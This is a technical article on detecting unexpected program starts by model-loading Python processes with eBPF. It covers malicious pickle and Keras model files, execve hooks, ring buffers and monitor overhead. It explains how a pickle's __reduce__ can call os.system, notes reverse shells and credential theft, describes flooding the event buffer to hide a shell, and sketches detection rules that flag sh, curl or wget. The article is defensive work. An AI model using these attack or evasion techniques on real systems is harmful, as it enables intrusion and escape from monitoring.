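# Detecting unexpected program starts by machine-learning workloads with eBPF, bpftrace and Falco

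## Why a model-loading process that starts a shell is a warning sign

A machine-learning workload is a process or container, usually running Python, that loads, trains or serves a model. Its work is mostly arithmetic on large arrays of numbers. It reads a model file from disk into memory and then answers requests. None of this ordinarily requires a command shell or a download tool such as curl or wget. If a Python process starts a shell just after opening a model file, the cause may be harmless, such as an unusual library, or it may be an attack contained in the file.

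On Linux, a monitor can detect every program start through eBPF, which runs small, checked programs inside the kernel when chosen events occur. Two tools that use eBPF are bpftrace, which compiles short tracing scripts, and Falco, an open-source monitor that checks kernel events against rules. Understanding either tool requires some knowledge of how Linux starts a program and how loading a file of model weights can cause it to start one.

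### How Linux starts a program

The kernel is the core of the operating system and controls the memory, disks and network. Everything else, including Python and the shell, runs in user space, where the processor blocks direct access to hardware and to the memory of other processes. To open a file or send data, a user-space program has to make a system call. It puts a number that identifies the request, along with the arguments, where the kernel expects them, and then executes an instruction that switches the processor into kernel code. The kernel checks whether the program may do this, does the work and returns a result. Python, C and shell scripts all make the same system calls.

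A process is a running instance of a program, with its own memory and process ID (pid). Starting another program normally takes two system calls. The process first copies itself with clone or the older fork, and the kernel gives the child a new pid and records its parent. The child runs the parent's program until it calls execve, which takes the path of a program file, a list of arguments (argv) and a set of environment variables. According to *EXECVE(2)* in the Linux Programmer's Manual, a successful call overwrites the calling process's code, data and stack with those of the new program. The call therefore returns only if it fails, in which case it returns −1 and the old program continues. "Program start" here means a successful call to execve or its variant execveat.

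The process keeps its pid and parent after the replacement. It usually keeps its user identity too, so a shell started by a model server can read whatever the server could read, including access keys. Files and network connections also stay open by default, according to the Linux Programmer's Manual. Attackers rely on this for a "reverse shell", which takes its input from a network connection to the attacker's machine and sends its output back over the same connection. The kernel does reset comm, its short name for a thread, to the name of the new executable, so a child that appeared as python3 now appears as sh.

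Python programs often clone themselves to work in parallel, and the copies keep running Python, so a clone without an execve is not a program start.

Python can start another program in several ways, but the function os.system matters most here. It takes a single string, like one typed at a terminal, which may contain several commands or feed the output of one into the next. The kernel cannot interpret such a string, because execve takes one file and a list of separate arguments. Python therefore passes the string to the C library function system, which starts the shell /bin/sh with the option -c and the string as its arguments. The shell interprets the string and starts the programs in it, so a call to os.system starts a shell even when the command names only one program. Python's subprocess module can instead start a program directly from a list of arguments, without a shell.

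### How loading a model can run code

A trained model consists mostly of numerical weights, but its file must also record how they fit together into Python objects. PyTorch, the main framework for developing models, does this with pickle, Python's own object format. According to PyTorch's *Serialization semantics*, a model is usually saved as a ZIP archive, with the large arrays in separate files and the pickled structure that links them in data.pkl. An attacker can make the model file run code by altering only data.pkl, without changing the weights.

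It is tempting to think of a pickle file as data in the way that a spreadsheet is data. It is closer to a small program. Kellas, Li and colleagues (2025), in *PICKLEBALL*, describe the interpreter for it, a simple machine inside Python's pickle module that works through a sequence of instructions and keeps its intermediate results on a stack. Four steps matter:

1. An import instruction gives the name of a module and of a function or class in it. The machine imports that object and puts it on the stack.
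2. Further instructions put the arguments on the stack.
3. An instruction named REDUCE makes the machine call the function with those arguments. The return value goes onto the stack in their place.
4. When the instructions run out, the machine returns whatever is on top of the stack as the loaded object.

The legitimate use of REDUCE is to rebuild objects that are awkward to store directly. The author of a class can write a method called `__reduce__` that returns a function and its arguments. Pickle writes the function's name and the arguments to the file when it saves the object, then calls the function to rebuild the object when it loads the file. A tensor class might use this to register a function that reads weights from disk. An attacker can instead write a `__reduce__` method that returns `os.system` and a command string. Pickle handles both cases identically, and the malicious file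 is well-formed.

The file need not contain hostile code in the ordinary sense. The Python documentation's *pickle* page explains that pickle stores functions by name only, so the code of os.system comes from the victim's own Python installation. The call happens during loading, before the caller has received a model, so never running the model afterwards is no protection. The load need not fail visibly, because later instructions can discard the number that os.system returns and then rebuild a working model.

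Pickle works this way by design. The Python documentation explains that unpickling imports any class or function named in the file by default, and advises readers to unpickle only data they trust. It also shows how to restrict imports to chosen names by overriding a method called `find_class`. There are safer formats, such as SafeTensors, which the model-sharing site Hugging Face released in 2022 and which stores little besides weights. But pickle is still common. Kellas and colleagues found in March 2025 that about 44.9% of Hugging Face repositories with at least 1,000 downloads a month contained a pickle model.

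### Restricted loading, and where it has failed

PyTorch applies the override idea to model files in a mode called `weights_only`. In this mode, the loader accepts only the functions and classes it needs to rebuild plain tensors and some basic types, and the file cannot make it import anything. The permitted names, listed in PyTorch's *_weights_only_unpickler.py*, include the framework's internal functions for rebuilding tensors, its parameter class and a couple of standard Python containers. Loading a file that names `os.system` therefore raises an error instead of starting a shell. Since version 2.6, `torch.load` has used this mode by default.

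Some callers turn off weights_only, the setting that limits which functions and classes a model file can use as it loads. Kellas and colleagues traced the models in 1,426 popular repositories that offered only pickle files, and in 219 of them (15.4%) at least one model needed a function or class outside the permitted set. Users downloaded those repositories 79.6 million times in one month. A user who meets the error can add the missing name to the allowlist or switch the restriction off. The error message includes instructions for both, and a warning to use them only with trusted files. Library maintainers sometimes make this decision for their users. The maintainers of flair, a text-processing library, disabled weights_only in their own loading function because their models would not load with it.

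The restricted mode has also been vulnerable. NVD's *CVE-2025-32434* records that in version 2.5.1 and earlier, an attacker could run commands through `torch.load` even with `weights_only` switched on. (NVD is the US government's National Vulnerability Database, and a CVE number identifies a published software flaw.) OSV's *CVE-2025-32434* (2025), an entry in a database of flaws in open-source software, rates it 9.3, or critical. In OSV's *GHSA-53q9-r3pm-6pq6*, the person who reported the flaw remarked that PyTorch's documentation described this setting as safe. PyTorch fixed the flaw in 2.6.0, the same release line that made restricted mode the default, so a server still running 2.5.1 loads models without restrictions by default, and an attacker can bypass its restricted mode.

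Another flaw became public on 27 January 2026, according to Ubuntu's *CVE-2026-24747* (2026). In PyTorch versions before 2.10.0, a crafted file could corrupt memory during a weights_only load and possibly run code, according to NVD's *CVE-2026-24747*. PyTorch's documentation lists memory corruption and denial of service as remaining risks of restricted loading. Restricted loading is still well worth using because it stops the ordinary os.system attack, but it cannot be the only protection between an untrusted file and the host.

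Avoiding pickle does not remove the risk either. Keras, another widely used framework, has its own format, an archive with a configuration file that describes the model's parts. NVD's *CVE-2025-1550* (2025) describes how an attacker could edit that file to name arbitrary Python functions and their arguments, which Keras then called while loading the model, even with its protective `safe_mode` setting on. INCIBE's *CVE-2025-1550* (2025), from Spain's national cybersecurity institute, lists the affected versions as 3.0.0 up to but not including 3.8.0. Much like REDUCE, the attack turns a name and some arguments in a file into a function call, but it uses a different loader, so a tool that parses only pickle would have had nothing to examine.

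### Why scanning the file is not enough

The usual defence on model-sharing sites is a static scanner, which examines a model file without loading it. For a pickle file, the scanner lists the functions and classes the file would import and compares them with a denylist of dangerous ones. This takes little compute and catches the obvious cases before anyone loads the file.

A denylist, though, covers only what somebody thought to include. Kellas and colleagues built two backdoored models that both got past two leading scanners. One used functions that the scanners had missed, and the other reached forbidden functions indirectly, through permitted ones. Scanners can also flag harmless models. Hugging Face's pickle scanner marks some imports in a popular flair model as suspicious, and the researchers had to manually review the model's operations and the library's source code to establish that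 the model was harmless. Few users will do such a review for every model they download.

Scanners also have to catch up with every new technique. *Lifecycle-Aware Dynamic Analysis for Secure ML Model Execution* (Digregorio, Di Gennaro and colleagues, 2026) uses the Keras flaw as an example. After its disclosure, Hugging Face adopted new detection rules from the security company Protect AI that referred to the flaw by number. Weeks later, other scanners on the same site still didn't flag files that exploited it. The paper proposes watching what an attack does to the host rather than examining how it is encoded in the file. It doesn't propose abandoning scanners, since they can reject files with known patterns before they run.

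Malicious code can enter through a pickle instruction, a Keras configuration entry or a corrupted block of memory, but once it is running, attackers tend to use it for the same few purposes. Kellas and colleagues list payloads that researchers have found in malicious pickle models on Hugging Face: some collected system details, some stole credentials and some opened reverse shells. A shell is convenient for all of these. A pickle instruction calls one function with some arguments, which is a clumsy way to write anything long, but a single call to os.system gives access to a whole command language and every tool on the machine. If the shell runs a download tool, the model file needs to carry only a short command, and the larger part of the attack can stay on a server, where scanners can't reach it and the attacker can change it at any time.

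Security vendors have begun to write rules on this basis. Elastic's *First Time Python Spawned a Shell on Host* raises an alert the first time in seven days that Python starts a shell with the -c option on a given machine. Elastic lists loading a model file as one possible cause, alongside malicious scripts and compromised packages, and considers a first occurrence highly suspicious because legitimate Python code rarely does this. This is the vendor's judgement, and the rule includes no counts to support "rarely". Its query also covers only macOS, so a Linux server needs a separate rule.

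### A test case

Suppose a python3 process with pid 4100 loads a harmless test pickle file in unrestricted mode. Loading it calls os.system with a command that uses curl to fetch a page from a web server on the same machine, then prints a word. The kernel handles four relevant system calls.

| System call | Affected process | comm afterwards | Parent |
|---|---|---|---|
| 4100 calls clone | 4207 (new) | python3 | 4100 |
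| 4207 calls execve | 4207 | sh | 4100 |
| 4207 calls clone | 4208 (new) | sh | 4207 |
| 4208 calls execve | 4208 | curl | 4207 |

Two of the four are program starts, sh in process 4207 and curl in process 4208. The parent of curl is the shell, so a monitor that looked only at direct children of Python would report sh and miss curl. To catch both, it has to follow the process ancestry, the chain of parents and grandparents, back to process 4100. The command has a second part so that the shell starts curl in a separate process. Given only a single simple command, some shells skip the second clone and call execve themselves, and sh and curl would then appear one after the other under the same pid, 4207.

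Nothing in the table depends on pickle. If the file had exploited the Keras flaw to call os.system with the same command, the kernel would have handled the same four calls.

### The detection idea and its two assumptions

The approach is to report every program started by a model-loading Python process or one of its descendants, unless the start is part of the workload's normal operation. This assumes that the attack starts a program and that the workload does not normally start that program.

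An attack doesn't have to start a program. Python can read files, open network connections and send data by itself, so code inside process 4100 can steal a credential without calling execve. A monitor of program starts would not detect this, so a lack of alerts doesn't show that the file was safe. Shells are convenient for attackers, so we can expect attacks to use them often, but not always. An attacker who starts curl directly from Python still causes a program start, as does one who replaces the Python process with a shell. The monitor should therefore cover all program starts, not just shells.

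Digregorio and colleagues give a reason to think that a workload's normal behavior is limited. Model files for the same framework are variations on what that framework can do, and within each phase of use (loading, inference or training) the framework interacts with the host in a narrow and predictable set of ways. A departure from that set is therefore a strong warning sign. The argument is about models, however, and a Python process may do much more than run one. Elastic lists build scripts, package installation and notebooks from which users run system commands among the likely sources of false alarms, and some serving software starts child processes of its own. A shell is hard to explain innocently on a server that loads one model and answers requests, but it may be routine on a data scientist's workstation.

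## How an eBPF program runs in the kernel and delivers events

A shell started by a malicious model file may run for only a few milliseconds, so a monitor that lists the running processes once a second would usually miss it. The kernel takes part in every program start, and eBPF lets it report each one as it happens, without changes to the kernel's source code. eBPF grew out of the Berkeley Packet Filter, a mechanism for selecting network packets, and entered Linux in 2014 with version 3.18. Kernel developers extended it to tracing in 2015 and to security checks in 2020.

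### From source code to alert

*BPF ring buffer* (Nakryiko, 2020) explains a small eBPF program that reports every program start on a machine. The version below is shorter and ignores processes that are not on a watch list.

```c
SEC("tp/sched/sched_process_exec")
int on_program_start(void *ctx)
{
    __u32 pid = bpf_get_current_pid_tgid() >> 32;
    if (!bpf_map_lookup_elem(&watched, &pid))
        return 0;                 /* not a watched process */

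    struct start *rec = bpf_ringbuf_reserve(&starts, sizeof(*rec), 0);
    if (!rec)
        return 0;                 /* no room in the buffer */

    rec->pid = pid;
    bpf_get_current_comm(rec->comm, sizeof(rec->comm));
    bpf_ringbuf_submit(rec, 0);
    return 0;
}
```

`watched` and `starts` are BPF maps, which hold data in the kernel between runs of the program. `watched` contains the pids of the model-loading process and its descendants. A companion program adds each child when its parent creates it. `starts` is a buffer for records being sent to user space.

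The Clang compiler translates this source into bytecode for a simple virtual machine with eleven 64-bit registers and a 512-byte stack. A user-space program called the loader then creates the maps and passes the bytecode to the kernel through a system call. By default, only privileged users may do this.

Before accepting the bytecode, the kernel checks it with the verifier, which simulates the possible paths through the code and tracks what each register and stack slot could contain. The verifier rejects any program it cannot show to be safe, such as one with a loop it cannot prove will end, a read from an uninitialised register, or an access outside permitted memory. In the example, `bpf_ringbuf_reserve` returns null when the buffer has no room. If the programmer deleted the `if (!rec)` test, the verifier would reject the program because one path would write to a null address. According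 to the Linux kernel documentation's *BPF ring buffer*, the verifier also tracks each reserved record and rejects any program that could fail to submit or discard one.

Nakryiko's record is too big for the small stack. It has 4 bytes for the pid, 16 for comm and 512 for the new program's path, or 532 bytes in total. His first version uses a map as scratch space, and a later one writes the record directly into reserved space in the buffer, as the code above does.

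Because of limits like these, eBPF tools do some of their work outside the kernel. *I Don't Care How You Hide It, I Care What You Do* (Ali and Case, 2026) describes ModelShield, a scanner that runs model files and traces their system calls. Its eBPF programs send fixed-size records containing the system call's number and raw arguments, and a user-space program interprets them later. When an argument is only the address of data in the process's memory, though, an eBPF program has to copy that data immediately, because the process may overwrite it before the user-space program gets the record.

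Once the bytecode has passed the verifier, the kernel's just-in-time compiler turns it into native machine instructions, and the loader attaches the result to a tracepoint. *A Study of Kernel Telemetry Options for Security-Oriented Provenance* (Houssel, Levillain and colleagues, 2026) explains that an unused tracepoint is an instruction that does nothing. When a program is attached, the kernel patches that instruction into a call. The kernel reaches the tracepoint used here after each successful execve.

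Take process 4207 from the earlier test case, the copy of Python that becomes a shell:

1. Process 4207 calls execve for /bin/sh. The kernel replaces the program, reaches the tracepoint and runs the eBPF code before the shell executes its first instruction.
2. The eBPF code calls a helper, one of a fixed set of kernel functions open to it, to get the current process's identity. The helper packs two numbers into one, and the shift by 32 bits extracts the pid.
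3. The code looks up 4207 in `watched`. If the pid were absent, the work would end here.
4. It reserves space in the buffer, fills in the pid and the name sh, and submits the record.
5. A user-space reader, which has been waiting on the buffer, wakes up and receives the record. It applies the monitor's rules and raises an alert if nothing in the workload's normal operation accounts for the shell.

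The shell runs without waiting for the fifth step, so it may already have started curl by the time anyone sees the alert. Preventing that requires a blocking mechanism such as an LSM hook.

### Two kinds of buffer

The older way to deliver records is the perf buffer, a set of buffers with one for each processor core. Each core writes only to its own buffer, so a burst of records on one core can overflow that buffer while the others are nearly empty. If an operator gives a 64-core server 8 MiB of perf buffer in total, each core gets 128 KiB. A single-threaded model load runs on one core at a time, so little more than 128 KiB may be available for its records.

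Separate per-core buffers can also deliver events out of order. Nakryiko wrote a monitor that tracked the creation, program start and exit of processes. Its records often arrived out of order because the kernel had moved short-lived processes between cores, and he had to add a good deal of logic to handle this. A monitor that follows process ancestry could receive the record of curl starting before the record of the shell creating that process, and curl would then seem unconnected to the model. ModelShield uses per-core buffers and keeps a separate store of parent–child links so that it can later assign out-of-order events to the right model operation.

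The BPF ring buffer, available since Linux 5.8, is a single buffer shared by all cores. The kernel reserves space in it for one record at a time, and the reader receives records in the order they were reserved. This has a small drawback, because a record that one core has reserved but not yet submitted delays all the records behind it. Nakryiko thinks perf buffers might still carry more data in theory at millions of events a second, but a monitor of program starts will never get near that rate. The ring buffer is the better choice for this job wherever the kernel supports it.

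### One build for many kernels

Monitoring often requires more than a process's pid and name. To find the parent, for example, an eBPF program can read `task_struct`, the large structure the kernel uses to describe the process. Kernel developers add, remove and reorder its fields between versions, so a program compiled to read the parent field at byte 1,500, say, would read unrelated data on a kernel where the field is elsewhere.

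BPF Type Format (BTF), a compact description of the kernel's data structures that many kernels include, solves this problem. Clang records in the compiled file that a given instruction needs the parent field of `task_struct`, rather than fixing the field's position. When the loader runs on the target machine, its library libbpf looks up the field in that kernel's BTF and corrects the instruction before the verifier checks it. Developers call this approach "compile once, run everywhere", or CO-RE.

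In *Agent-Warden*, Cui, Gu and colleagues (2026) used it for a monitor that tracks the processes and files of AI agents, and they ran the monitor on both Intel-compatible and ARM machines. It doesn't let every program run on every kernel, however, because BTF can relocate a field but can't supply a field or an attachment point that an older kernel never had.

### Losing events

Events are lost when the eBPF program produces records faster than the reader removes them. If the ring buffer is full, the program's attempt to reserve space fails immediately and the traced process continues. This is the right behaviour for a server, which should not stall because its monitor is slow, but the event will be missing from the evidence.

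*WOOTdroid* (2026), a paper on tracing Android devices, describes pipelines based on the kernel's ftrace facility in which new entries silently overwrite the oldest. A slow reader therefore loses the beginning of an incident, whereas with an eBPF ring buffer it would lose the end. *WOOTdroid* treats this loss as a correctness problem rather than a performance problem, because one missing network connection can break the chain between a suspicious download and its destination.

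How quickly the buffer fills depends mostly on what the monitor traces. If each record takes 512 bytes, including the 8-byte header that the kernel adds, an 8 MiB buffer holds 8,388,608 / 512 = 16,384 records. While the reader is completely stalled, perhaps because the machine is short of processor time, a monitor that traces every system call might produce 50,000 records a second on a busy server, and one that traces only program starts might produce 20.

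| Buffer size | Records held | Time to fill at 50,000 a second | Time to fill at 20 a second |
|---|---|---|---|
| 256 KiB | 512 | 0.01 s | 26 s |
| 8 MiB | 16,384 | 0.33 s | 819 s |
| 64 MiB | 131,072 | 2.6 s | 6,554 s |

At 8 MiB the reader of the full trace has a third of a second to recover, and the reader of program starts has over thirteen minutes. Even a 256 KiB buffer gives the execve-only monitor ten times as long as 64 MiB gives the other. (The eBPF Docs' *Map type BPF_MAP_TYPE_RINGBUF* page requires a size that is a power of two and a multiple of the memory page size, typically 4,096 bytes. All three sizes qualify.)

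A larger buffer helps when the reader stalls briefly, but not when it is always too slow. If 50,000 records arrive each second and the reader handles 40,000, the 8 MiB buffer fills in about 1.6 seconds, and from then on the monitor loses a fifth of all events. Doubling the buffer delays the losses by only another 1.6 seconds.

An attacker can exploit the difference by putting code in a model file that makes harmless system calls in a tight loop until the shared buffer overflows, and then starts a shell. The attacker hopes that the kernel will drop the record of the shell starting. If the monitor recorded only execve calls, the attacker would have to flood the buffer with program starts, and the first few would already have raised alerts.

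Tracing more system calls can catch attacks that never start a program, but it takes more engineering. According to Ali and Case, a single call to `torch.load` can generate thousands of system calls. Inside the kernel, ModelShield discards events from unrelated processes. A separate process drains the buffer continuously while the model runs, so a model crash doesn't destroy the evidence. A monitor that needs both program starts and other system calls could put program starts in their own ring buffer, where file reads can't crowd them out.

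When the buffer is full, the example program at the start of this section returns without recording the loss, so the operator never learns that a program start went missing. Nakryiko points out that libbpf can report lost records for perf buffers but not for ring buffers. The eBPF program should therefore add one to a counter in a map whenever a reservation fails, and the program that reads the buffer should check the counter regularly. Only 20 records a second are expected, so any loss deserves an alert.

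### How ptrace, audit and seccomp compare

Linux had other ways to watch or filter system calls before eBPF. The oldest in common use is ptrace, which lets one process trace another. At each system call, the kernel stops the traced process and wakes the tracer, which reads the arguments, including any text they point to, and then lets the process continue. This gives a very detailed view, but constantly switching between the two processes is slow. Digregorio and colleagues built their model scanner on ptrace and measured between 0.001 and 3.2 seconds of tracing overhead on a laptop, depending on the framework and phase. They consider ptrace suitable for scanning a file before use but recommend a mechanism with less overhead for live monitoring.

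A process can also have only one tracer at a time. Houssel and colleagues note that a malicious process can take the tracer's place itself, which prevents the monitor from attaching. An eBPF program on a tracepoint avoids this problem because it doesn't attach to the process. It covers every process on the host, including those in containers, which share the host's kernel.

The audit subsystem is a logging facility inside the kernel. An administrator writes rules that select system calls, and the kernel sends matching records to a user-space service, usually auditd. For execve, the records include the program's path and argv, so audit suits a server that needs only a log of program starts. It is less suitable for large volumes or complex conditions. Houssel and colleagues explain that its developers intended it for targeted audits rather than continuous recording of a whole system, and that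 any filtering beyond the built-in rules has to happen in user space. By then the kernel has already produced and copied each record. Cui and colleagues identify this copying and switches between processes as sources of overhead in older audit-based monitors.

Seccomp filters system calls rather than recording them. A process installs a filter on itself, its later children inherit it, and the filter decides whether each system call may go ahead. The filter runs entirely in the kernel without waking another process, so its overhead can be low. When Python tries to start /bin/sh, the filter receives the system call number for execve and the arguments as plain numbers. The first argument is the memory address where the text "/bin/sh" begins, and the filter can't read the text at that address. It can therefore block execve altogether, but it can't allow one program and refuse another.

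Letting a seccomp filter read the text would not make its decision safe, because another thread in the same process could replace a harmless path with /bin/sh after the filter had checked it and before the kernel used it. An eBPF program that reads the text on entry to the call is vulnerable to the same attack. Houssel and colleagues found that 282 of the 407 system calls in Linux 6.14 accept at least one address of this kind. Hooks that run later, after the kernel has made its own copy, are much safer.

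Seccomp also doesn't keep a record of earlier calls. *Enforcement of In-Kernel Stateful Security Policies via eBPF* (Galletta, 2026) describes a process that has just opened the system's password file. A seccomp filter can't take this into account when the next call arrives, but an eBPF program can record the first event in a map and look it up at the second. The watch list in the example relies on this too.

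### What monitoring costs

Each time an event occurs, the attached eBPF program uses processor time, and the process that caused the event waits for it to finish. Houssel and colleagues measured this overhead on a 24-core machine running Linux 6.1. With a tracepoint program on entry to the relevant system calls, total processor time rose by 1.43% for a web server handling 50,000 connections, 1.22% for 50,000 successive runs of the echo command, and 8.63% for writing 50,000 files. The echo test is the closest to monitoring program starts, although its probes recorded the creation of each process rather than the execve that followed.

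Cui and colleagues tested their monitor on Linux 6.8 with a deliberately busy workload that repeated a cycle of process creation, program starts, and file reads, writes and renames 1,000 times, all of which the monitor traced. On an ARM machine, the workload took 3.5% longer with the monitor running. On a fast AMD desktop processor, it took 0.2% to 1.1% longer, depending on how the monitor stored its state. The AMD results varied by more than a percentage point between rounds, so the true slowdown there may be close to zero.

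Monitors that also enforce a policy can have similarly low overhead. *GoLeash* (2025) restricts what the components of a Go program may do. It slowed the main server of Kubernetes, a system for managing containers, by 2.1% under a stream of read requests.

These percentages apply to the workloads tested, and overhead depends more on the number of events than on the tool. *Waiting at the front door* (2026), a study of monitors for network delays, reports that the packet-tracing tool pwru had an overhead of about 1.5% with probes on a few selected kernel functions and upwards of 25% with probes on every function that handles packets. By a rough calculation for program starts, if each event takes 2 microseconds to process, 20 events a second use 0.004% of one core and 50,000 use 10%. An execve-only monitor should therefore add almost no overhead to a model server, but this is an estimate that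 would need testing on the machine in question.

The nature of the work also helps limit tracing overhead. Multiplying two matrices of 4,096 by 4,096 numbers takes almost 69 billion multiplications, but none needs a system call, because the numbers are already in the process's memory and the processor can read, multiply and store them without the kernel. The process needs the kernel when it reads a file, obtains more memory, creates a thread or communicates with a graphics processor's driver. Digregorio and colleagues found that tracing overhead had little to do with model size during inference but grew roughly in line with it during loading, because a bigger file takes more read calls. Monitoring system calls therefore cannot show whether the arithmetic is correct, since a model altered to give wrong answers makes the same calls as the original.

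### What the monitor has to trust

The verifier protects the kernel from faulty eBPF programs, but it does not protect the monitor from an attacker who already controls the machine. Cui and colleagues assume that the hardware, the kernel, the verifier and the privileged program that loads the monitor are sound. Galletta also assumes the compiler is sound, excludes attacks on the kernel and bugs in the verifier, and requires the monitor to be in place before the workload starts. Ali and Case assume that the attacker begins without administrator (root) access.

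The operator partly controls whether that last assumption holds. If the process that loads a malicious model runs as root on the host, the payload can stop the reader, detach the eBPF programs or delete its own pid from the watch list. Running the model server as an ordinary user, with the reader outside its container, removes the easy ways to do this. The reader should also send each alert to another machine immediately, so an attacker who gains root a few seconds later can't erase the record of the first shell.

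## Where the kernel can report a program start

The example program in the previous section ran at a single tracepoint, after a successful execve. An eBPF program can also run at other points during the call, and different information is available at each. Choosing the wrong point can produce alerts for programs that never started, or records with an empty command line.

### One execve call from entry to return

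Process 4207, the copy of Python that is about to become a shell, calls execve with the filename /bin/sh and an argv of three strings: sh, -c and the command. The order of events below follows Android's copy of the Linux source code for execve.

The kernel first reaches the tracepoint `sys_enter_execve`, before it has done any work on the request. The process's `comm` is still `python3`. The eBPF program gets the addresses of the filename and `argv`, so it has to copy the text from the process's memory. It can find the parent through `task_struct`, here and at every later hook. The call has no return value yet, so the program can't determine whether it will succeed.

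The entry hook is convenient because it provides the old comm and the new filename together, which is nearly all that a rule against Python starting download tools needs. *eBPF for Security Monitoring* builds a small monitor on this hook, and one line of the sample output shows a process named python3 about to run /usr/bin/wget.

The variant execveat has its own tracepoint, sys_enter_execveat, so a monitor that works at entry needs both this tracepoint and the one for execve. *execsnoop.py* (Gregg and Xing, 2016), a script that lists program starts, attaches only to execve. The filename passed to execveat can also be an empty string, because the caller may identify the program by the number of an open file instead.

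After entry, the kernel copies the filename into its own memory, opens the file and checks that execution is allowed. If the file doesn't exist, the call fails at this step. Otherwise the kernel copies the environment and argv into the memory it is preparing for the new program.

The kernel then reaches the LSM hook bprm_check_security, where security modules can allow or refuse the program start, so a monitor here can refuse a start as well as report it. The process's comm is still python3, but the kernel has now resolved the path of the file it will run. Aqua Security's *security_bprm_check*, part of the documentation for the monitoring tool Tracee, gives this resolved path as a reason to use the hook. On Debian and Ubuntu, /bin/sh normally links to the dash shell, so an entry hook reports /bin/sh where this one can report /usr/bin/dash.

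Arguments are harder to get at this point. According to Android's *lsm hooks*, a copy of the kernel's own description, argv is reliably available to a security module. But argv is still in memory prepared for the new program, which the process isn't using yet, so an eBPF program can't simply read it from the current process. Tracee takes argv from the entry hook instead.

One execve call can also trigger the LSM hook more than once. If the file is a script whose first line names /bin/sh as its interpreter, the kernel runs the hook for the script and then again for the shell. A monitor that counts every hook run as a program start would count this execve call twice.

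The kernel then commits to the new program. It ends any other threads in the process, replaces the memory and changes comm to sh. A failure from here on kills the process instead of returning an error to it. Newer kernels have a tracepoint just before these changes, sched_prepare_exec, which Elver (2024), in *[PATCH v2] tracing: Add sched_prepare_exec tracepoint*, proposed. Like the entry hook, it records both the old comm and the new filename, but it doesn't fire for attempts that have already failed. Elver's sample output shows sshd, the remote-login server, about to become /bin/bash.

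The sched_process_exec tracepoint, used in the earlier example, fires once the switch is complete. It covers both execve and execveat. Elver's sample output shows three fields: filename, pid and old_pid. The record doesn't include argv, but the eBPF program can read it from the new program's memory. In a reply on a kernel mailing list, Steve (2020) suggested this tracepoint for anyone who only wants information about program starts.

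The old comm is no longer available at this point. To report that python3 became sh, the monitor has to store the earlier name in a map, for example when the parent creates the child.

The field old_pid matters when a thread other than the main one calls execve. That thread survives and takes over the main thread's ID, so a monitor that matches records by thread ID can fail to link records from before and after the call. Matching by process ID avoids this.

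The last point is sys_exit_execve, or sys_exit_execveat for the variant, where the return value is available. After a failure, the process is still python3 and the value is a negative error number, such as −2 for a missing file. After a success, the value is 0 and comm is sh, but the memory that held the original arguments is gone. To report the arguments and the return value together, a monitor has to save the arguments at entry. Gregg and Xing's script sends them to user space, where it matches them with the return value by pid.

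Even a return value of 0 doesn't prove that a program started. A caller can pass execveat the AT_EXECVE_CHECK flag, which makes the kernel check whether it would allow the file to run and then return without running it. If the check passes, the call returns 0, but sched_process_exec doesn't fire.

| Hook | Filename | argv | Return value | comm | Parent | Failed attempts included |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
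| sys_enter_execve, sys_enter_execveat | As the caller gave it | In the caller's memory | No | Old | Yes | All |
| bprm_check_security | Resolved path | Copied, but hard to read | No | Old | Yes | Those that fail at or after this hook |
| sched_process_exec | Yes | In the new program's memory | No, but the call has succeeded | New | Yes | None |
| sys_exit_execve, sys_exit_execveat | Only if saved at entry | Only if saved at entry | Yes | New after success, old after failure | Yes | All that return an error |

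For a monitor that only reports, sched_process_exec is the best default. The main cost is the extra map for the old comm.

### Failed attempts

When a Python program uses the subprocess module to run curl without specifying its directory, Python calls execve once for each directory in PATH, in order, until a call succeeds. If PATH begins with /usr/local/sbin, /usr/local/bin, /usr/sbin and /usr/bin, and curl is only in /usr/bin, the first three calls fail and the fourth succeeds. A monitor at the entry hook therefore reports curl four times for one program start.

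Failed execve calls are common enough in ordinary use to matter. Debian's *execsnoop_example.txt* lists 14 execve calls from routine system services, of which 3 failed because the program didn't exist at the given path. Gregg and Xing's script omits failed calls unless the user asks for them. Gregg (2018) warns in *execsnoop.bt(8)* that the bpftrace tool of the same name doesn't trace the return value, so its output may include calls that failed. An operator who copies one of these tools should check which version it is.

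Failed attempts to start a program can still be evidence. If a model server's container doesn't include curl, a malicious file's direct attempts to start curl all fail, and a monitor at sched_process_exec reports none of them. It makes sense to count the model server's failed attempts separately, group them by program name and give them a lower priority than successful program starts. A failed attempt to run curl is worth investigating if it comes from a process that should never need curl.

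Counting failed executions requires the entry and exit hooks, because the later hooks miss the most common failure, a missing file, which ends the call before the kernel reaches bprm_check_security. Tracee has a dedicated event for failed executions, but according to Aqua Security's *process execute failed*, it covers only failures in a later part of the call, so it would also miss the three failed searches for curl.

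### Arguments that are not yet in memory

Linux loads only part of a program into memory when it starts, and makes many pages available only when something first uses them. That first access causes a page fault, and the kernel pauses the process while it fetches the page. An eBPF program on an ordinary system-call tracepoint can't wait in this way. If the page isn't in memory yet, the helper that reads the process's memory returns an error and leaves zeros in the destination, according to a reader's comment in *Access user space data without sleeping* (danobi, 2020).

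The result can be a record with a blank filename for an ordinary call. Deslauriers reported this in LTTng, another Linux tracer, for a filename written as a constant in a test program. The developers suspected that nothing had yet loaded the page containing the constant when the tracer tried to read it. The same could happen with os.system, because the path /bin/sh is a constant inside the C library, and the monitor may try to read that page before anything else in the process has used it.

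An eBPF program should check the helper's return value and mark an argument as unreadable when the read fails. Otherwise, someone investigating an alert can't tell a failed read from an empty argument.

Kernel developers have been working on a more direct solution. Torvalds, in *Merge tag 'trace-v6.13'*, describes groundwork in Linux 6.13 that allows page faults in the code behind system-call tracepoints, though eBPF programs could not yet use it. Yatsenko (2026), in *bpf: Add support for sleepable tracepoint programs*, added that support, so an eBPF program at system-call entry can wait for a page and then read it reliably. Maintainers have since accepted the work into the main kernel, and Marlière (2026), in *[PATCH 7.1.y] selftests/bpf*, proposed adding its tests to the 7.1 series.

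Munduruca's *[SRU][R][PATCH 1/1] UBUNTU* proposed reverting part of the change in an Ubuntu kernel, so distributions may still differ. A monitor that has to run on many servers can't yet rely on this feature.

Arguments read at entry may also differ from those the kernel uses, so the monitor should read them at sched_process_exec, after the kernel has copied them. Blank arguments are much less likely at that point because the kernel has just written the pages that contain them.

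### Children that run before the monitor knows about them

A monitor that follows process ancestry has to put each new child on its watch list before the child does anything. The obvious method is to wait for clone to return in the parent, because the return value is the child's pid. Dileo (2021), in *Some Musings on Common (eBPF) Linux Tracing Bugs*, an analysis for the security company NCC Group, explains why this fails. In the test case, events can happen in this order:

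1. Process 4100 calls clone, and the kernel creates process 4207.
2. The kernel marks 4207 as ready to run, and another processor core picks it up.
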